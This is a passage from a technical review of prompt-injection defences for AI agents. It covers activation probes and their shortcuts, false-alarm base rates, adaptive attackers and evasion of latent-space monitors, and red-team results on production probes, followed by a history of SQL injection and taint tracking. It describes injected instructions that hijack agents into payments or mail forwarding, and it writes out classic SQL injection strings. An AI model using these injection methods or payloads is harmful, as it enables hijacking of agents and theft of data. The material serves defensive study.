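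A fair test has to compare cases that share the same moment. In AgentDojo's bill-paying task, the bill file contains a block of text that is addressed to the agent and signed with the user's name. The block asks for a transfer to the attacker. Kale and Vishwanath kept the rest of the conversation and varied the file:

- The **clean twin** is the same moment from a run with no attack, so the file contains only the bill.
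- The **harmless look-alike** keeps the block and the signature, but the text inside is a notice that a planning review has moved to Friday.
- The **harmless instruction** is a plain sentence for a human reader, such as a request to bring a laptop to a workshop.
- The **plain-text attack** is the attacker's request without the block around it.

A good probe should flag the original attack and the harmless instructions, but not the clean twins or look-alikes. In applications it had trained on, the standard probe flagged a median of 80% of clean twins, 98% of look-alikes and 90% of harmless instructions at the default threshold of 0.5.

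The 80% figure is the most striking because a clean twin contains nothing suspicious. It is this high because the training data included no runs without an attack. Nearly every time the agent had just opened the bill file in training, the file was poisoned, so the probe learned to associate that moment with an attack.

The standard probe also detects the injection itself, in part. Its median AUROC for ranking an attack above its clean twin was 0.87. Position alone would give 0.5 on this comparison, and the seven-number baseline, which can still use length, scored 0.65 to 0.75. However, the shortcut raises the probe's score above the threshold at many harmless moments.

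### Training with matched negatives

The remedy is to add training examples in which the shortcut gives the wrong answer. For each attack in the formatted block, Kale and Vishwanath added its clean twin and a look-alike as negatives, and the plain-text attack as a positive. They also added every moment of the clean runs. The twins make position uninformative, and the look-alikes do the same for formatting. No probe was trained on harmless instructions, so testing on them shows whether the remedy generalizes to a kind of example absent from training.

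They also changed the classifier to a logistic regression with a penalty on large weights, which discourages it from fitting accidental details. The table shows the two changes separately. Each cell gives the median percentage over six models, first for the training applications and then for new ones. The last row counts only attacks that the agent carried out, and uses a stricter threshold that flags 1% of ordinary tool outputs in the training applications.

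| | Standard probe | New classifier, standard data | New classifier, matched negatives |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clean twins flagged | 80 / 70 | 59 / 39 | 17 / 6 |
| Look-alikes flagged | 98 / 94 | 95 / 81 | 11 / 10 |
| Harmless instructions flagged | 90 / 82 | 81 / 58 | 33 / 15 |
| Plain-text attacks flagged | 98 / 95 | 97 / 89 | 96 / 58 |
| Successful attacks caught | 79 / 80 | 91 / 69 | 95 / 82 |

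In seen applications, the new classifier reduces false alarms on clean twins from 80% to 59%, and the new data, which includes matched negatives, reduces them further to 17%. Detection of successful attacks rises from 79% to 95%, mostly because of the classifier.

Adding clean twins and look-alikes separately shows which shortcut each removes. Clean twins alone cut false alarms on twins from 57% to 22%, while the same number of clean moments from other positions cut them only to 45%. Look-alikes alone cut false alarms on look-alikes from 96% to 12%, but 37% of twins were still flagged. Both additions were needed to get both false-alarm rates low.

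In new applications, false alarms stay low, but the matched probe flags only 58% of plain-text attacks at the default threshold because all its scores are lower. It catches 82% of successful attacks, ranging from 69% for Gemma-4-31B to 94% for Qwen3-8B. For four of the six models, most of the missed attacks were ones the agent had ignored anyway. The uncertainty is large because only 48 to 163 test attacks per model succeeded in seen applications, and 111 to 318 in new ones. On these numbers, the matched probe was clearly better than the standard one in new applications for two models and clearly worse for two.

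The probe probably still relies on some shortcuts. AgentDojo reuses the same attacker account throughout an application, so a probe can learn the account number or email address. That can't help in a new application, where the accounts are different, which may partly explain why detection falls there. Training on harmless notices in one format also only partly prevents false alarms in other formats. When Kale and Vishwanath put harmless notices behind a "TODO" or a fake system-message label, formats for which the probe had seen no harmless examples, it flagged 49% of them in applications seen in training, compared with 11% in the familiar format.

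Text classifiers show the same limit. In *PIDS-Bench*, Shire and Kim (2026) supplemented the training data of two text detectors with harmless prompts that resemble attacks. False alarms nearly disappeared on test prompts written in the same style, but largely remained on security-related prompts from public collections. Shire and Kim chose the public prompts to be difficult, so the result provides little evidence about everyday mail. It still suggests that a team should collect harmless look-alikes from its own traffic instead of writing them.

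### Would a text filter do as well?

If the training data matters this much, a classifier that uses only the text might be enough. Kale and Vishwanath built a simple one that counts words and word pairs in the latest tool output and doesn't use the model. It has no information about position in the conversation, but when trained on the standard data, it still learned the formatting shortcut and flagged 81% of look-alikes in seen applications. When trained with matched negatives, it flagged 4%.

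On AgentDojo's own attacks, this filter ranked attacks above their clean twins slightly better than the probe did, with an AUROC of 0.99 compared with 0.98 in seen applications and 0.92 in new ones. This is some evidence that detection doesn't require access to a model's internals, though counting words is unusually effective on AgentDojo because its templates are so repetitive. The probe was better at ranking plain-text attacks, and its threshold also transferred better to a new application. With thresholds from the training applications, the probe caught 82% of successful attacks in the new application and the text filter caught 38%. When both thresholds came from the new application's own traffic, the text filter caught 87% and the probe 74%.

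Kale and Vishwanath did not compare their probe with the larger text detectors that companies release. Liu (2026) tested fifteen of these detectors on harmless and injected tool outputs in *Passing the Test You Trained On*. One of them, PIGuard, gave the maximum score of 1.00 to a message confirming a password change. With thresholds set so that each detector flagged 1% of harmless inputs, PIGuard caught 95.1% of the injections in BIPIA, a collection of attacks in emails, tables and code, but only 2.1% of those in AgentDojo. PIGuard's training data contained 1,116 complete BIPIA inputs. The best detector, from Horizon-Labs, caught 82.2% of the injections in AgentDojo and all of those in a second agent benchmark. Horizon-Labs had trained it on agent-style inputs that shared no data with either benchmark.

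Fomin, by contrast, found that activation probes beat several text detectors on indirect injections at equal false-positive rates. It is therefore unsettled whether activations or text are better for detecting injections, but in all three studies detectors worked best on inputs whose form resembled their training data.

### How many alarms are real

Even a probe without shortcuts has to cope with the rarity of attacks. Let π be the share of tool results that contain an attack, *t* the share of attacks the probe flags, and *f* its false-positive rate. By Bayes' theorem, the share of alarms that are real is

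π*t* / (π*t* + (1 − π)*f*).

Take a probe that catches 95% of attacks and flags 1% of harmless results, and run it on a million tool results:

| Attack rate | Attacks | Caught | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 10,000 | 9,500 | 9,900 | 49% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 1,000 | 950 | 9,990 | 8.7% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 100 | 95 | 9,999 | 0.9% |

The probe is the same in every row, and only the traffic differs.

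Real attack rates vary at least as widely as those in the table. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening*, found hidden injections in about 1% of some 200,000 résumés, which matches the table's first row. Khodayari and colleagues found a rate on the open web far below the one in the bottom row. More than 90% of the résumé injections contained no explicit instruction, so a probe trained on commands might miss many of them.

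People often overlook this effect when they judge a test by its accuracy, an error called the *base-rate fallacy*. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, applied it to software that searches computer logs for intrusions. He imagined a small office network that logs about 100,000 events a day, two of them intrusions. Even a detector that catches every intrusion must keep its false-positive rate near 1 in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. At 1 in 1,000, it raises about 100 false alarms a day, and only 2% of its alarms are real.

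In the journal version of *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, Axelsson drew on studies of operators in power stations and paper mills and concluded that most people would stop trusting a device by the time half its alarms were false. More than twenty years later, Erbacher (2022) found in *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity* that the field still had no clear understanding of what counts as a low false-alarm rate.

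An injection probe has one advantage over Axelsson's detector because its alarms usually go to another model instead of a person who gets tired. Sending all million tool results to a second model at one second each would take about 278 hours. In the bottom row of the table, the probe cuts this to under three hours but misses five of the 100 attacks. That is a good way to save computation, even though more than 99% of the alarms are false.

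False alarms are a much bigger problem for a probe that blocks tool results by itself, because an agent reads several results per task and one false alarm can be enough to stop the whole task. One of Liu's text detectors flagged 3.2% of AgentDojo's harmless outputs, which would have stopped 10.3% of the tasks.

A second check doesn't eliminate the problem either. If it wrongly confirms 1% of the harmless results it receives, then in the bottom row it would block about 100 harmless results along with at most 95 attacks. The number of harmless results blocked may well be higher, because the second model is likely to misclassify the same harmless text that the probe misclassifies.

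Benchmarks are also too small to show that a detector's false-positive rate, *f*, is low enough for use when attacks are rare. If one input in 10,000 is an attack, *f* has to be about 1 in 10,000 for half the alarms to be real. Liu obtained 339 harmless tool outputs from AgentDojo's tasks, and the Horizon-Labs detector flagged none of them. Even if the outputs were independent, this result would be compatible with a true false-positive rate of almost 0.9%.

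### Choosing a threshold

A higher threshold means fewer second checks but more missed attacks. Kale and Vishwanath measured this tradeoff, assuming that 1% of tool results carry an attack. In seen applications at the default threshold, the standard probe sent a median of 315,000 of every million results to the second check, and the matched probe sent 74,000. At one second per check, the standard probe's results would take about 88 hours to check and the matched probe's about 21. With the stricter threshold from the table above, the matched probe sent 21,000 and caught 95% of successful attacks, down from 99% at the default.

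The choice between the stricter setting and the default depends on how much harm an attack could do. Returning to the default would add about 53,000 checks per million results. The agents fell for roughly 18% of attacks, so a million results would contain about 1,800 successful ones. The extra four percentage points of detection would stop about 70 of them, or one for every 750 or so added checks. That is probably worthwhile for an agent that can make bank transfers. If attacks were a hundred times rarer, stopping each one would take about 75,000 checks, or some 20 hours of a second model's time.

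A team can set a threshold without any examples of attacks by running the probe on ordinary traffic and picking the score that only 1% of inputs exceed. This assumes that the traffic is harmless. If 1% of the résumés in a pile contain injections, the top 1% of scores might come mostly from attacks, and the threshold would be far too high.

The chosen false-alarm rate may not hold on other tasks. Kale and Vishwanath's threshold, set to flag 1% of ordinary results, flagged 11% for one Nemotron model when the user tasks changed within the same applications. Alarms would also increase if more ordinary tool outputs contained harmless instructions. They estimate that if half did, as might happen in a busy inbox, the matched probe's 21,000 checks would grow to 73,000.

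A strict threshold can also hide a probe's reliance on a shortcut. When Kale and Vishwanath set the threshold on a new application's own traffic, the standard probe caught 87% of successful attacks and the matched probe 74%, with a similar number of checks. The threshold was high enough to exclude most clean twins but not most successful attacks. A team with plenty of representative traffic might therefore do well with the standard probe, as long as the traffic stays the same.

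## How well do activation probes hold against attackers who adapt?

The usual test of a probe estimates how often its score exceeds the detection threshold on a fixed set of attacks that researchers happened to collect. An attacker needs only one text that hijacks the agent while scoring below the threshold, and can search for it. The probe can flag 99% of the test set while many such texts exist, because the test set covers a tiny part of what a person or a program could write. An attacker who gets feedback can also build on the attempts that came closest.

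An attacker can probably lower a probe's score without spoiling the attack, because Abdelnabi and colleagues' results suggest that probes mainly measure whether the model has been exposed to an injection, not whether it complies. If a probe instead measured what makes the model obey, text changed to lower the score would also fail to hijack the agent.

### Twelve published defences

The best-known evidence on adaptive attacks mostly concerns defences other than activation probes. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues attacked twelve published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection. They tailored their attacks to each defence and used both automated search and human attackers. Their success rate was above 90% for most of the defences, whereas most of the original papers had reported rates near zero.

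Six of the twelve defenses were detectors. Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor screen the text. DataSentinel has a second model repeat a secret key while reading the text, and raises an alarm if the model fails. MELON runs the agent again with the user's request hidden and checks whether it makes the same tool call, which would suggest the call came from the data. None of the six uses a probe trained on the agent's activations. Circuit Breakers comes closest, but it is a training method that disrupts the activations leading to harmful output and does not flag attacks.

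The paper therefore doesn't measure how well an activation probe would hold against attackers who adapt. But the twelve defences had little in common except good results on fixed attacks, and those results predicted almost nothing about how the defences would do against adaptive ones. Anyone who expects probes to be an exception needs a specific reason.

Attention Tracker, which monitors a model's attention weights, is closer to a probe. In *A Critical Evaluation of Defenses against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025), Jia, Shao and colleagues found that it had an AUROC of 1.00 on standard tests but missed 69% of the attacks in another test. Both results are possible because a threshold that suits one test can be wrong for a new kind of attack. An attacker who knows about this weakness can send the kind of attack the detector misses.

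Bailey, Serrano and colleagues showed in *Obfuscated Activations Bypass LLM Latent-Space Defenses* (ICLR 2026) that attackers can optimise inputs so that a model's activations look harmless to a monitor while the model still misbehaves.

### Attackers with and without the probe

Dong and colleagues also tested their probes against adaptive attacks and got a much more encouraging result, with AUROC staying between 0.956 and 1.000. Their result differs from Bailey and colleagues' mainly because their attackers had no access to the probe, so they could not tell whether a change of wording lowered its score. An attack revised only to be more persuasive is still a planted instruction in a tool result, which is what the probe learned to recognise, and it might even be easier to recognise.

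This is decent evidence that making attacks better at fooling the model doesn't also make them evade a probe, but weak evidence about how a probe performs against someone trying to fool it. AUROC averages over attacks, whereas an attacker will send the one with the lowest score.

How easily an attacker can get access depends on the model. With an open model, an attacker can plant attacks in sample text, compute the activations on their own hardware, and train a substitute probe from a published recipe, all without stealing anything. Text that evades the substitute might well evade the defender's probe too, though this isn't certain. Dong and colleagues' probes transferred well between benchmarks and languages, which suggests that separately trained probes pick up similar signals.

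With a closed model, the attacker can't compute activations and can only observe how the agent behaves. If the agent visibly stops whenever the probe fires, each attempt still reveals whether the score was above the threshold. The company can reveal less by responding in ways the attacker can't see, and it can ban accounts that keep triggering alarms. These advantages depend on keeping the probe secret, but in the threat model that Narisetty and colleagues describe, the attacker knows the defences. Replacing a leaked probe may not help much, because a new one trained on the same data would probably find a similar direction.

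### Probes in production

Two companies have described the probes they use in products. Google DeepMind's probes, described in *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (Kramár, Engels and colleagues, 2026), detect misuse, specifically requests for help with cyberattacks, rather than prompt injection. In misuse, the attacker is the user, and the model may be following its instructions correctly. Kramár, Engels and colleagues found that existing probe designs struggled when inputs were much longer than the training examples. They developed designs that handle length better, and they recommend pairing a probe with a language model that checks the difficult cases. The length problem should concern anyone who probes agents, because an agent's prompt grows with every tool result, but the paper gives no figures for injection.

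Anthropic publishes figures for prompt injection in its models' system cards. The *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 4.8 defines the probes as "lightweight detectors trained on internal model representations", so they read activations. Later cards describe only the probes' purpose.

Its main test uses Shade, an automated attacker built by the security firm Gray Swan. Shade tries to hijack a coding agent in 40 scenarios, with 200 attempts at each, or 8,000 attempts per model. A scenario counts as breached if any attempt succeeds. The first four rows below come from the Opus 4.8 card and from Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5, published in July. The last four come from a September card in which Anthropic introduced a stronger version of Shade. All the models used extended thinking.

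| Model | Attacker | Successful attempts without probes | With probes | Scenarios breached without probes | With probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8 | Older Shade | 7.03% | 2.09% | 23 | 15 |
| Opus 5 | Older Shade | 0.56% | 0.18% | 13 | 4 |
| Sonnet 5 | Older Shade | 0.31% | 0.09% | 7 | 5 |
| Mythos 5 | Older Shade | 0.45% | 0.41% | 8 | 11 |
| Opus 5 | Stronger Shade | 90.93% | 18.21% | 40 | 40 |
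| Fable 5 | Stronger Shade | 86.87% | 34.09% | 40 | 39 |
| Fable 5.1 | Stronger Shade | 56.87% | 12.80% | 38 | 36 |
| Sonnet 5 | Stronger Shade | 19.47% | 15.76% | 36 | 35 |

Against the older attacker, probes stopped around 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded on Opus 4.8, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5. On Mythos 5 they made almost no difference. The success rates there correspond to about 36 successful attempts without probes and 33 with them, and the number of scenarios in which at least one attack succeeded went up. That rise may be due to chance, because the two conditions were run separately and a scenario in which attacks rarely work may be breached in one run and not the other. Too few attacks succeeded to show whether Mythos 5's probes are useless or just somewhat worse than the others.

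Anthropic gives these reductions without a false-alarm rate, so readers can't tell how much legitimate work the safeguards interrupt. With safeguards on, attacks succeeded more often on Opus 4.8 than on its predecessor (2.09% against 0.43%), but Anthropic considers the newer model a better balance between robustness and false positives.

Probes helped less when the agent operated a computer through its screen. In a similar test with 14 scenarios, they reduced the attack success rate per attempt on Opus 4.8 from 7.14% to 5.11%, but the number of breached scenarios rose from seven to eight. Anthropic traces the extra breach to a scenario in which one attempt out of 200 succeeded with safeguards on and none succeeded with them off.

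### The stronger attacker

Gray Swan trained the new Shade for longer and on more varied attacks, and its results on the same 40 scenarios were very different. Against Opus 5, Shade succeeded in 91% of attempts without probes and 18% with them, and it breached every scenario at least once in both cases.

Part of the rise from 0.56% to 90.93% had nothing to do with the attacker. In the September tests, a separate classifier that screens for dangerous cybersecurity requests could pass a request to Opus 4.8, which then answered instead of Opus 5. Anthropic reran the older Shade in this arrangement and also corrected an error in the thinking settings of earlier tests. Shade's success rate on Opus 5 was then 2.68%, compared with 0.56% in July, and Opus 4.8 had answered 57% of the requests that got a valid response. The rest of the rise, from 2.68% to 90.93%, came with the stronger attacker, and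 some of its attacks succeeded against Opus 5 itself.

For Fable 5.1 the fallback accounts for everything. The stronger Shade failed on all 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered directly. Its successes were all among the 64% or so that went to Opus 4.8, which means that it hijacked Opus 4.8 in roughly nine out of ten of those. In May, the older Shade had succeeded against the same model in 7% of attempts. (The requests that trigger the classifier are not a random sample, so the two rates aren't strictly comparable, but selection is unlikely to explain a gap that large.)

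Sonnet 5 provides the cleanest comparison, because Opus 4.8 answered no requests when Anthropic reran the older attacker. With probes on, the success rate against Sonnet 5 rose from 0.09% for the older attacker to 15.76% for the stronger one, and the share of attacks the probes stopped fell from about 70% to 19%. On Opus 5, the probes stopped 80% of even the stronger attacks. Anthropic doesn't explain the difference. Sonnet 5 may already resist the cruder attacks, which are also the easiest for a probe to recognise, so the attacks that get through would tend to be ones the probe also misses.

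None of these attackers had trained against the probes, as far as Anthropic reports. Gray Swan trained both versions of Shade on earlier Claude models and ran them unchanged on the newer ones. The attacker could still refine its text over the 200 attempts, so this test is harder than a fixed list of attacks. It is easier than the attacks by Nasr and colleagues, who tailored theirs to each defence. In the one-week contest that Gray Swan ran for the Opus 4.8 card, people attacked Claude models live, with prizes for success. The models ran without their probes, so the contest didn't show how well the probes hold against human attackers.

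Anthropic argues that the Shade tests deliberately favour the attacker, who practises on the same scenarios used for the test and gets many attempts at each. Real attackers usually don't know the target's setup, and repeated attempts make it more likely that somebody notices. This argument is fair for an attack on one particular company but less convincing for widely sold products, since an attacker can subscribe to the same coding agent, build a plausible project around it and practise there.

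### What repetition does to a success rate

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p* and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*.

For Opus 4.8 with probes, *p* is 2.09%. With *k* = 200, the formula predicts that Shade would breach 98.5% of the scenarios, or about 39 of the 40. It actually breached 15 (37.5%).

The formula goes wrong because it uses one *p* for every scenario, whereas some targets are much harder to attack than others, as the figures for Opus 4.5 already suggested. Shade's successes, about 167 in total, all fell in those 15 scenarios, an average of 11 each. In each of the other 25, it failed all 200 times. If the true rate there had been 2.09%, each scenario would have had only a 1.5% chance of 200 straight failures, so 25 such runs would have been very unlikely. Let *pᵢ* be the rate in scenario *i*. The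 expected share of breached scenarios is the average of 1 − (1 − *pᵢ*)^*k*. Because this curve flattens as *pᵢ* rises, that average can't exceed the value for the average rate, so using the average rate for every scenario can overestimate the expected share but never underestimate it.

The clustering of successful attacks is partly good news for a defender. More attempts at the 25 resistant scenarios might have achieved little, although 200 failures are still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 1.5%, which would be enough for a patient attacker. In the 15 weak scenarios, the average success rate with probes was nearly 6%, so an attacker who found one would need about 18 attempts on average. A team deploying the agent generally doesn't know which group its setup belongs to, and an attacker who can choose between targets will look for the weak ones.

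Against the stronger Shade, the clustering no longer offers any protection. An attacker gets through Opus 5's probes in 18% of attempts, compared with nearly every attempt without them, so a successful attack takes about five times as many tries. Whether that matters depends on how much effort or money each try takes, and emailing another poisoned invoice takes almost none.

An attacker can also make many attempts without trying the same target twice by sending bulk mail. Anthropic gives the example of one email sent to a thousand inboxes. At 2.09% per inbox, the attacker would expect about 21 successes. Agents set up in similar ways will tend to resist or obey the same email together, which makes the number of successes vary more but does not lower the expected number. A bulk mailer would usually do worse than Shade, having never practised on these inboxes, but 21 successes would yield a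 lot of forwarded mail for the effort of sending a thousand emails.

### Zero breaches in 129 browser scenarios

Anthropic's July card reports tests of agents that browse the web in 129 simulated environments, with ten attempts at each. Without safeguards, attacks breached 11 of the environments on Opus 5 and 71 on Mythos 5. With *auto mode* switched on, they breached none on either model. The Decoder covered the result under the headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*, though the article adds that the result holds only with auto mode on.

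Auto mode combines the probes, which inspect incoming content, with a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls. The classifier could have stopped attack A, the email asking for all mail to go to a stranger, even if the probes had missed it. Anthropic compared auto mode only with no safeguards, so the result doesn't show how much each part contributed. This matters because Claude Cowork, the product in the test, always runs the probes but does not always run auto mode. The July and September browser tests include no figures for probes alone.

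The sample size also limits what zero breaches can show. If the 129 environments were a random draw from all the situations such an agent meets, zero breaches would be compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true rate of up to 2.3% of situations. A true rate of 1% would produce no breaches more than a quarter of the time. Successes cluster by scenario here too, so it would be wrong to treat all 1,290 attempts as independent and get a bound ten times lower. Anthropic also selected the environments, rather than drawing them at random, so that the agent always encounters the attack. In that respect, the test is harder than ordinary browsing.

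The origin of the attacks is a bigger limitation than the sample size. Professional attackers developed them against an older model, Opus 4.7, and Anthropic then replayed them on the newer ones. The zero is strong evidence that auto mode stops good attacks designed for a different target. On Mythos 5, it stopped every attack in a set that had worked in more than half of the environments. But nobody reports searching for new attacks with auto mode switched on, as an adaptive test would require.

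Later results are consistent with a very low but nonzero breach rate. On a revised set of 110 environments, Anthropic again recorded no breaches with auto mode for Opus 5, Sonnet 5 or Fable 5.1, but one for Fable 5, in a case where Opus 4.8 had answered instead. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5.5, the successor to Opus 5, reports similar or better results than Opus 5's on every injection test it includes. Anthropic expects auto mode to hold up because an attack would have to get past the probes and the classifier separately. This makes a successful attack harder to find, and much harder if the two layers tend to miss different attacks, but an attacker could still find one.

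## What did taint tracking achieve in ordinary software, and where did it leak?

Long before language models existed, programmers had to choose between recognising attacks and designing software to prevent them. SQL injection is the clearest example, because programmers have used both approaches against it for more than twenty years.

### SQL injection and parameterised queries

SQL is the language in which programs send commands to a database. Suppose a website lets suppliers look up their own invoices. A supplier types a name, and the program joins it to the rest of the command:

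```
query = "SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE supplier = '" + name + "'"
```

If the name is `Acme`, the database returns Acme's invoices. If an attacker types `x' OR '1'='1`, the database receives this:

```
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE supplier = 'x' OR '1'='1'
```

The quotation mark after the `x` ends the name early, and the rest of the input becomes part of the command. Since 1 always equals 1, the database returns everybody's invoices.

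One defence is a filter that rejects or cleans suspicious input. Rejecting quotation marks stops this attack, but it also blocks legitimate supplier names such as O'Brien. It doesn't protect a field that expects an invoice number, where an attacker can enter `1 OR 1=1` to get the same effect without quotation marks.

The other defence is a *parameterised query*. The program first sends the command with a placeholder:

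```
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE supplier = ?
```

The database first parses this text, which fixes what the command does. The program then supplies the name, which the database treats only as a value to compare. Given the attacker's input, it searches for a supplier literally called `x' OR '1'='1` and finds none. The database treats every other input the same way, so it is guaranteed that no input can change the command.

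In *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems*, CISA (the US government's cybersecurity agency) and the FBI (2024) describe input filters as brittle, difficult to enforce at scale and frequently bypassed. They recommend parameterised queries, which the MySQL database has supported since 2004. This is expert judgement, not a measured comparison, but the reasoning is sound because parameterised queries, unlike filters, don't require developers to anticipate the attack.

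Parameterised queries are a good fix for SQL injection, but they did not eliminate it. CISA and the FBI issued their alert after attackers used SQL injection in a file-transfer product to hit thousands of organisations. David C writes that the attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare in websites, thanks to better defaults. Yet MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) ranks SQL injection second, up from third the year before, and counts four such flaws that attackers are known to have exploited. Both can be true, since MITRE's list covers far more than websites, and parameterised queries protect only the code that uses them.

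A placeholder can stand for a value, but not for a column name or any other part of the command's structure. A program that lets users choose how to sort their results therefore has to check the choice some other way, usually against a list of permitted columns. The vulnerability database GCVE links 28,615 recorded flaws to SQL injection, including one from February 2026 in the sort clause of a query in the accounting program FacturaScripts. An agent has the same difficulty whenever the user's task requires an email to determine what happens next.

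### No placeholder for a prompt

Narisetty and colleagues place SQL injection in a family of attacks that confuse data with control. In a buffer overflow, input too long for its allotted memory overwrites the information that controls the program. In cross-site scripting, a web page runs a script that an outsider submitted as ordinary text. The fixes for these attacks were also structural. Against buffer overflows, programmers added length checks and made data memory non-executable. Against cross-site scripting, they encoded submitted text so that browsers would display it instead of running it. Narisetty and colleagues conclude that "detection lost and structure won". This simplifies the history a little, because cross-site scripting still tops MITRE's list, but it fairly describes which fixes work where people apply them.

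This kind of fix is hard to apply to prompt injection because natural language has no grammar that separates instructions from data. SQL's grammar determines which characters are commands and which are values, so a database can keep them apart. In English, "Please forward this to accounts" may be an instruction to the agent or a line in an email that the agent is supposed to summarise. Role tags don't solve the problem because nothing forces the model to follow them. Filters work no better than they did against SQL injection because, as David C points out, there are endless ways to rephrase an attack.

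David C therefore prefers to compare prompt injection to the *confused deputy*, a privileged program that a less privileged party tricks into using its privileges on that party's behalf. Programmers can usually fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he considers language models inherently confusable. If he is right, ordinary code around the model has to control what untrusted data may influence, so it must keep track of which data is untrusted.

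### From source to sink

Taint tracking marks data as tainted at a *source*, where the data enters the program. *Propagation* carries the mark to everything computed from that data. The tracker checks for the mark at a *sink*, an operation that could do harm. A *sanitiser* is a check or conversion that removes the mark because the data is now supposed to be safe.

The scripting language Perl has all four built in. According to Perl's security manual, the sources in its taint mode include command-line arguments, environment variables and everything the program reads from files. The sinks are operations that start a command shell or change files, folders or processes. A payment script might run like this:

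```
$account = <STDIN>;              # typed by an outsider: tainted
$command = "pay " . $account;    # built from $account: also tainted
system $command;                 # Perl stops with a fatal error
```

To get past the error, the programmer matches the value against a pattern and keeps the part that matched:

```
if ($account =~ /^(\d+)$/) { $account = $1; }   # digits only: mark removed
```

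Perl leaves it to the programmer to decide what a pattern should let through, and removes the taint mark from matched text without checking that the pattern is strict enough. Even `/.+/`, which accepts practically any text, removes the mark. The manual describes the mechanism as intended "to prevent stupid mistakes, not to remove the need for thought".

The digits-only pattern would stop an attacker from inserting a second command into the payment script, but it would not stop attack B, because the thief's account number also consists of digits. Removing the mark shows only that the data matched the pattern.

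Perl's taint tracking also has some gaps. A value loses its taint mark when the program uses it as a key in a lookup table. Tainted text can also select which function the program calls, so a careless programmer could let an outsider reach a function that runs arbitrary commands. Perl's designers accepted such gaps because they assumed that the programmer was honest and the users were untrustworthy. For running a stranger's code, the manual recommends a separate module that confines it to a restricted compartment.

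### TaintDroid

The same technique can protect confidentiality if the mark means "private" and the sink is the network. *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert and colleagues, 2014) modified Android to follow private data through unmodified apps. Every variable carries 32 extra bits, one for each kind of private data, so a value computed from the phone's location and its number carries two marks. The marks follow data between variables, in messages between apps, and into files. TaintDroid doesn't track data inside the phone's built-in machine-code libraries, but it marks their results afterwards. Apps can add marks but never remove them. TaintDroid records what leaves the phone and where it goes, but doesn't block anything.

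In 2010, Enck and colleagues used TaintDroid to test 30 popular apps, chosen at random from 358 that could use the internet and at least one of the location, camera and microphone. Fifteen sent the user's location to advertising or analytics servers without consent. Seven collected the device's identification number, in some cases along with the phone number and the SIM card's serial number. Two thirds of the apps handled private data suspiciously. The team compared TaintDroid's reports with recorded network traffic and found no false alarms, but without the apps' source code they could not tell how many leaks it had missed. Two years later, eight of the fifteen apps that had sent locations were still available, and three of them were still seen doing so.

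TaintDroid slowed a processor-heavy benchmark by 32%, or by 18% with Android's run-time compiler switched off. The original 2010 version, from before Android had that compiler, had an overhead of 14%. Users would hardly have noticed, since an app took 91 milliseconds to open instead of 79, and taking a photo took less than 1% longer. Messages between apps slowed the most, with a message of 100 numbers taking more than three times as long. Earlier trackers that followed every machine instruction slowed programs more, by a factor of 2 to 20.

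### Labels, integrity and noninterference

A tracker needs a rule for data that comes from several sources. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, gave a general one. Write *A* → *B* if information with label *A* may flow to a place with label *B*. For any two labels, the *join* *A* ⊕ *B* is the lowest label that both may flow to. If a program computes a value from inputs labelled *A* and *B* and stores it in a place labelled *C*, the rule is

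*A* ⊕ *B* → *C*.

In a database of medical, financial and criminal records, each label is a set of these categories. Information may flow only to a place whose label includes every category in the information's own label, and the join of two labels is their union. A report that draws on a medical file and a bank statement is therefore labeled {medical, financial}, and it cannot go to somebody cleared only for medical data.

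A *lattice* is an ordering in which any two labels have a lowest common upper label and a highest common lower one. Denning derived this structure from modest consistency requirements. For example, if *A* → *B* and *B* → *C*, then *A* → *C* must hold too, because a program could move the data in two permitted steps. This means that a system that checks each step has also checked every sequence of steps.

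Denning's examples concern secrecy, but the same mathematics works for integrity with the direction reversed. Trusted data may flow anywhere, but untrusted data may not flow into trusted places, and the join of the two labels is "untrusted". Kenneth Biba developed this version in the 1970s. As Narisetty and colleagues explain it, a program that reads data below its own integrity level drops to that level, and no program may write to anything above its level. In the invoice example, the agent starts out trusted, drops when it opens the inbox, and is then no longer allowed to pay anyone. In a modern version of the idea, a model that processes a party's information should have only that party's privileges. David C quotes this version from an online discussion between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista.

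These rules are a means to an end, and Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined the end itself without mentioning labels. They called it *noninterference*: one group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group sees. Let *w* be the sequence of all commands that all users have given, and let *w*∖*G* be the same sequence with the commands of group *G* deleted. Then *G* does not interfere with user *v* if

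out(*w*, *v*) = out(*w*∖*G*, *v*) for every *w*,

where out is what the system displays to *v* afterwards. The system has to behave, as far as *v* can tell, as though *G* had never touched it. Goguen and Meseguer's first example amounts to a statement about integrity. If the commands that write to or delete a file do not interfere with a user, then none of them can change what that user reads from it.

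For a program with trusted inputs *u*, untrusted inputs *x* and trusted outputs *T*, the integrity form is

*T*(*u*, *x*) = *T*(*u*, *x*′) for every *u*, *x* and *x*′.

Under this property, two runs that differ only in their untrusted inputs produce the same trusted outputs. The strictest guarantee for agents treats their consequential actions as the trusted outputs, so those actions must be the same in both runs.

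### A leak through a branch that never runs

Noninterference compares two runs, but a tracker that works while the program is running sees only one. This makes *implicit flows* hard to catch. In an explicit flow, the program copies data or computes something from it. In an implicit flow, information passes through the choice of which branch to run. Denning discusses a short program by J. S. Fenton, rewritten here with a variable called `secret`:

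```
b = false
c = false
if not secret:  c = true
if not c:       b = true
```

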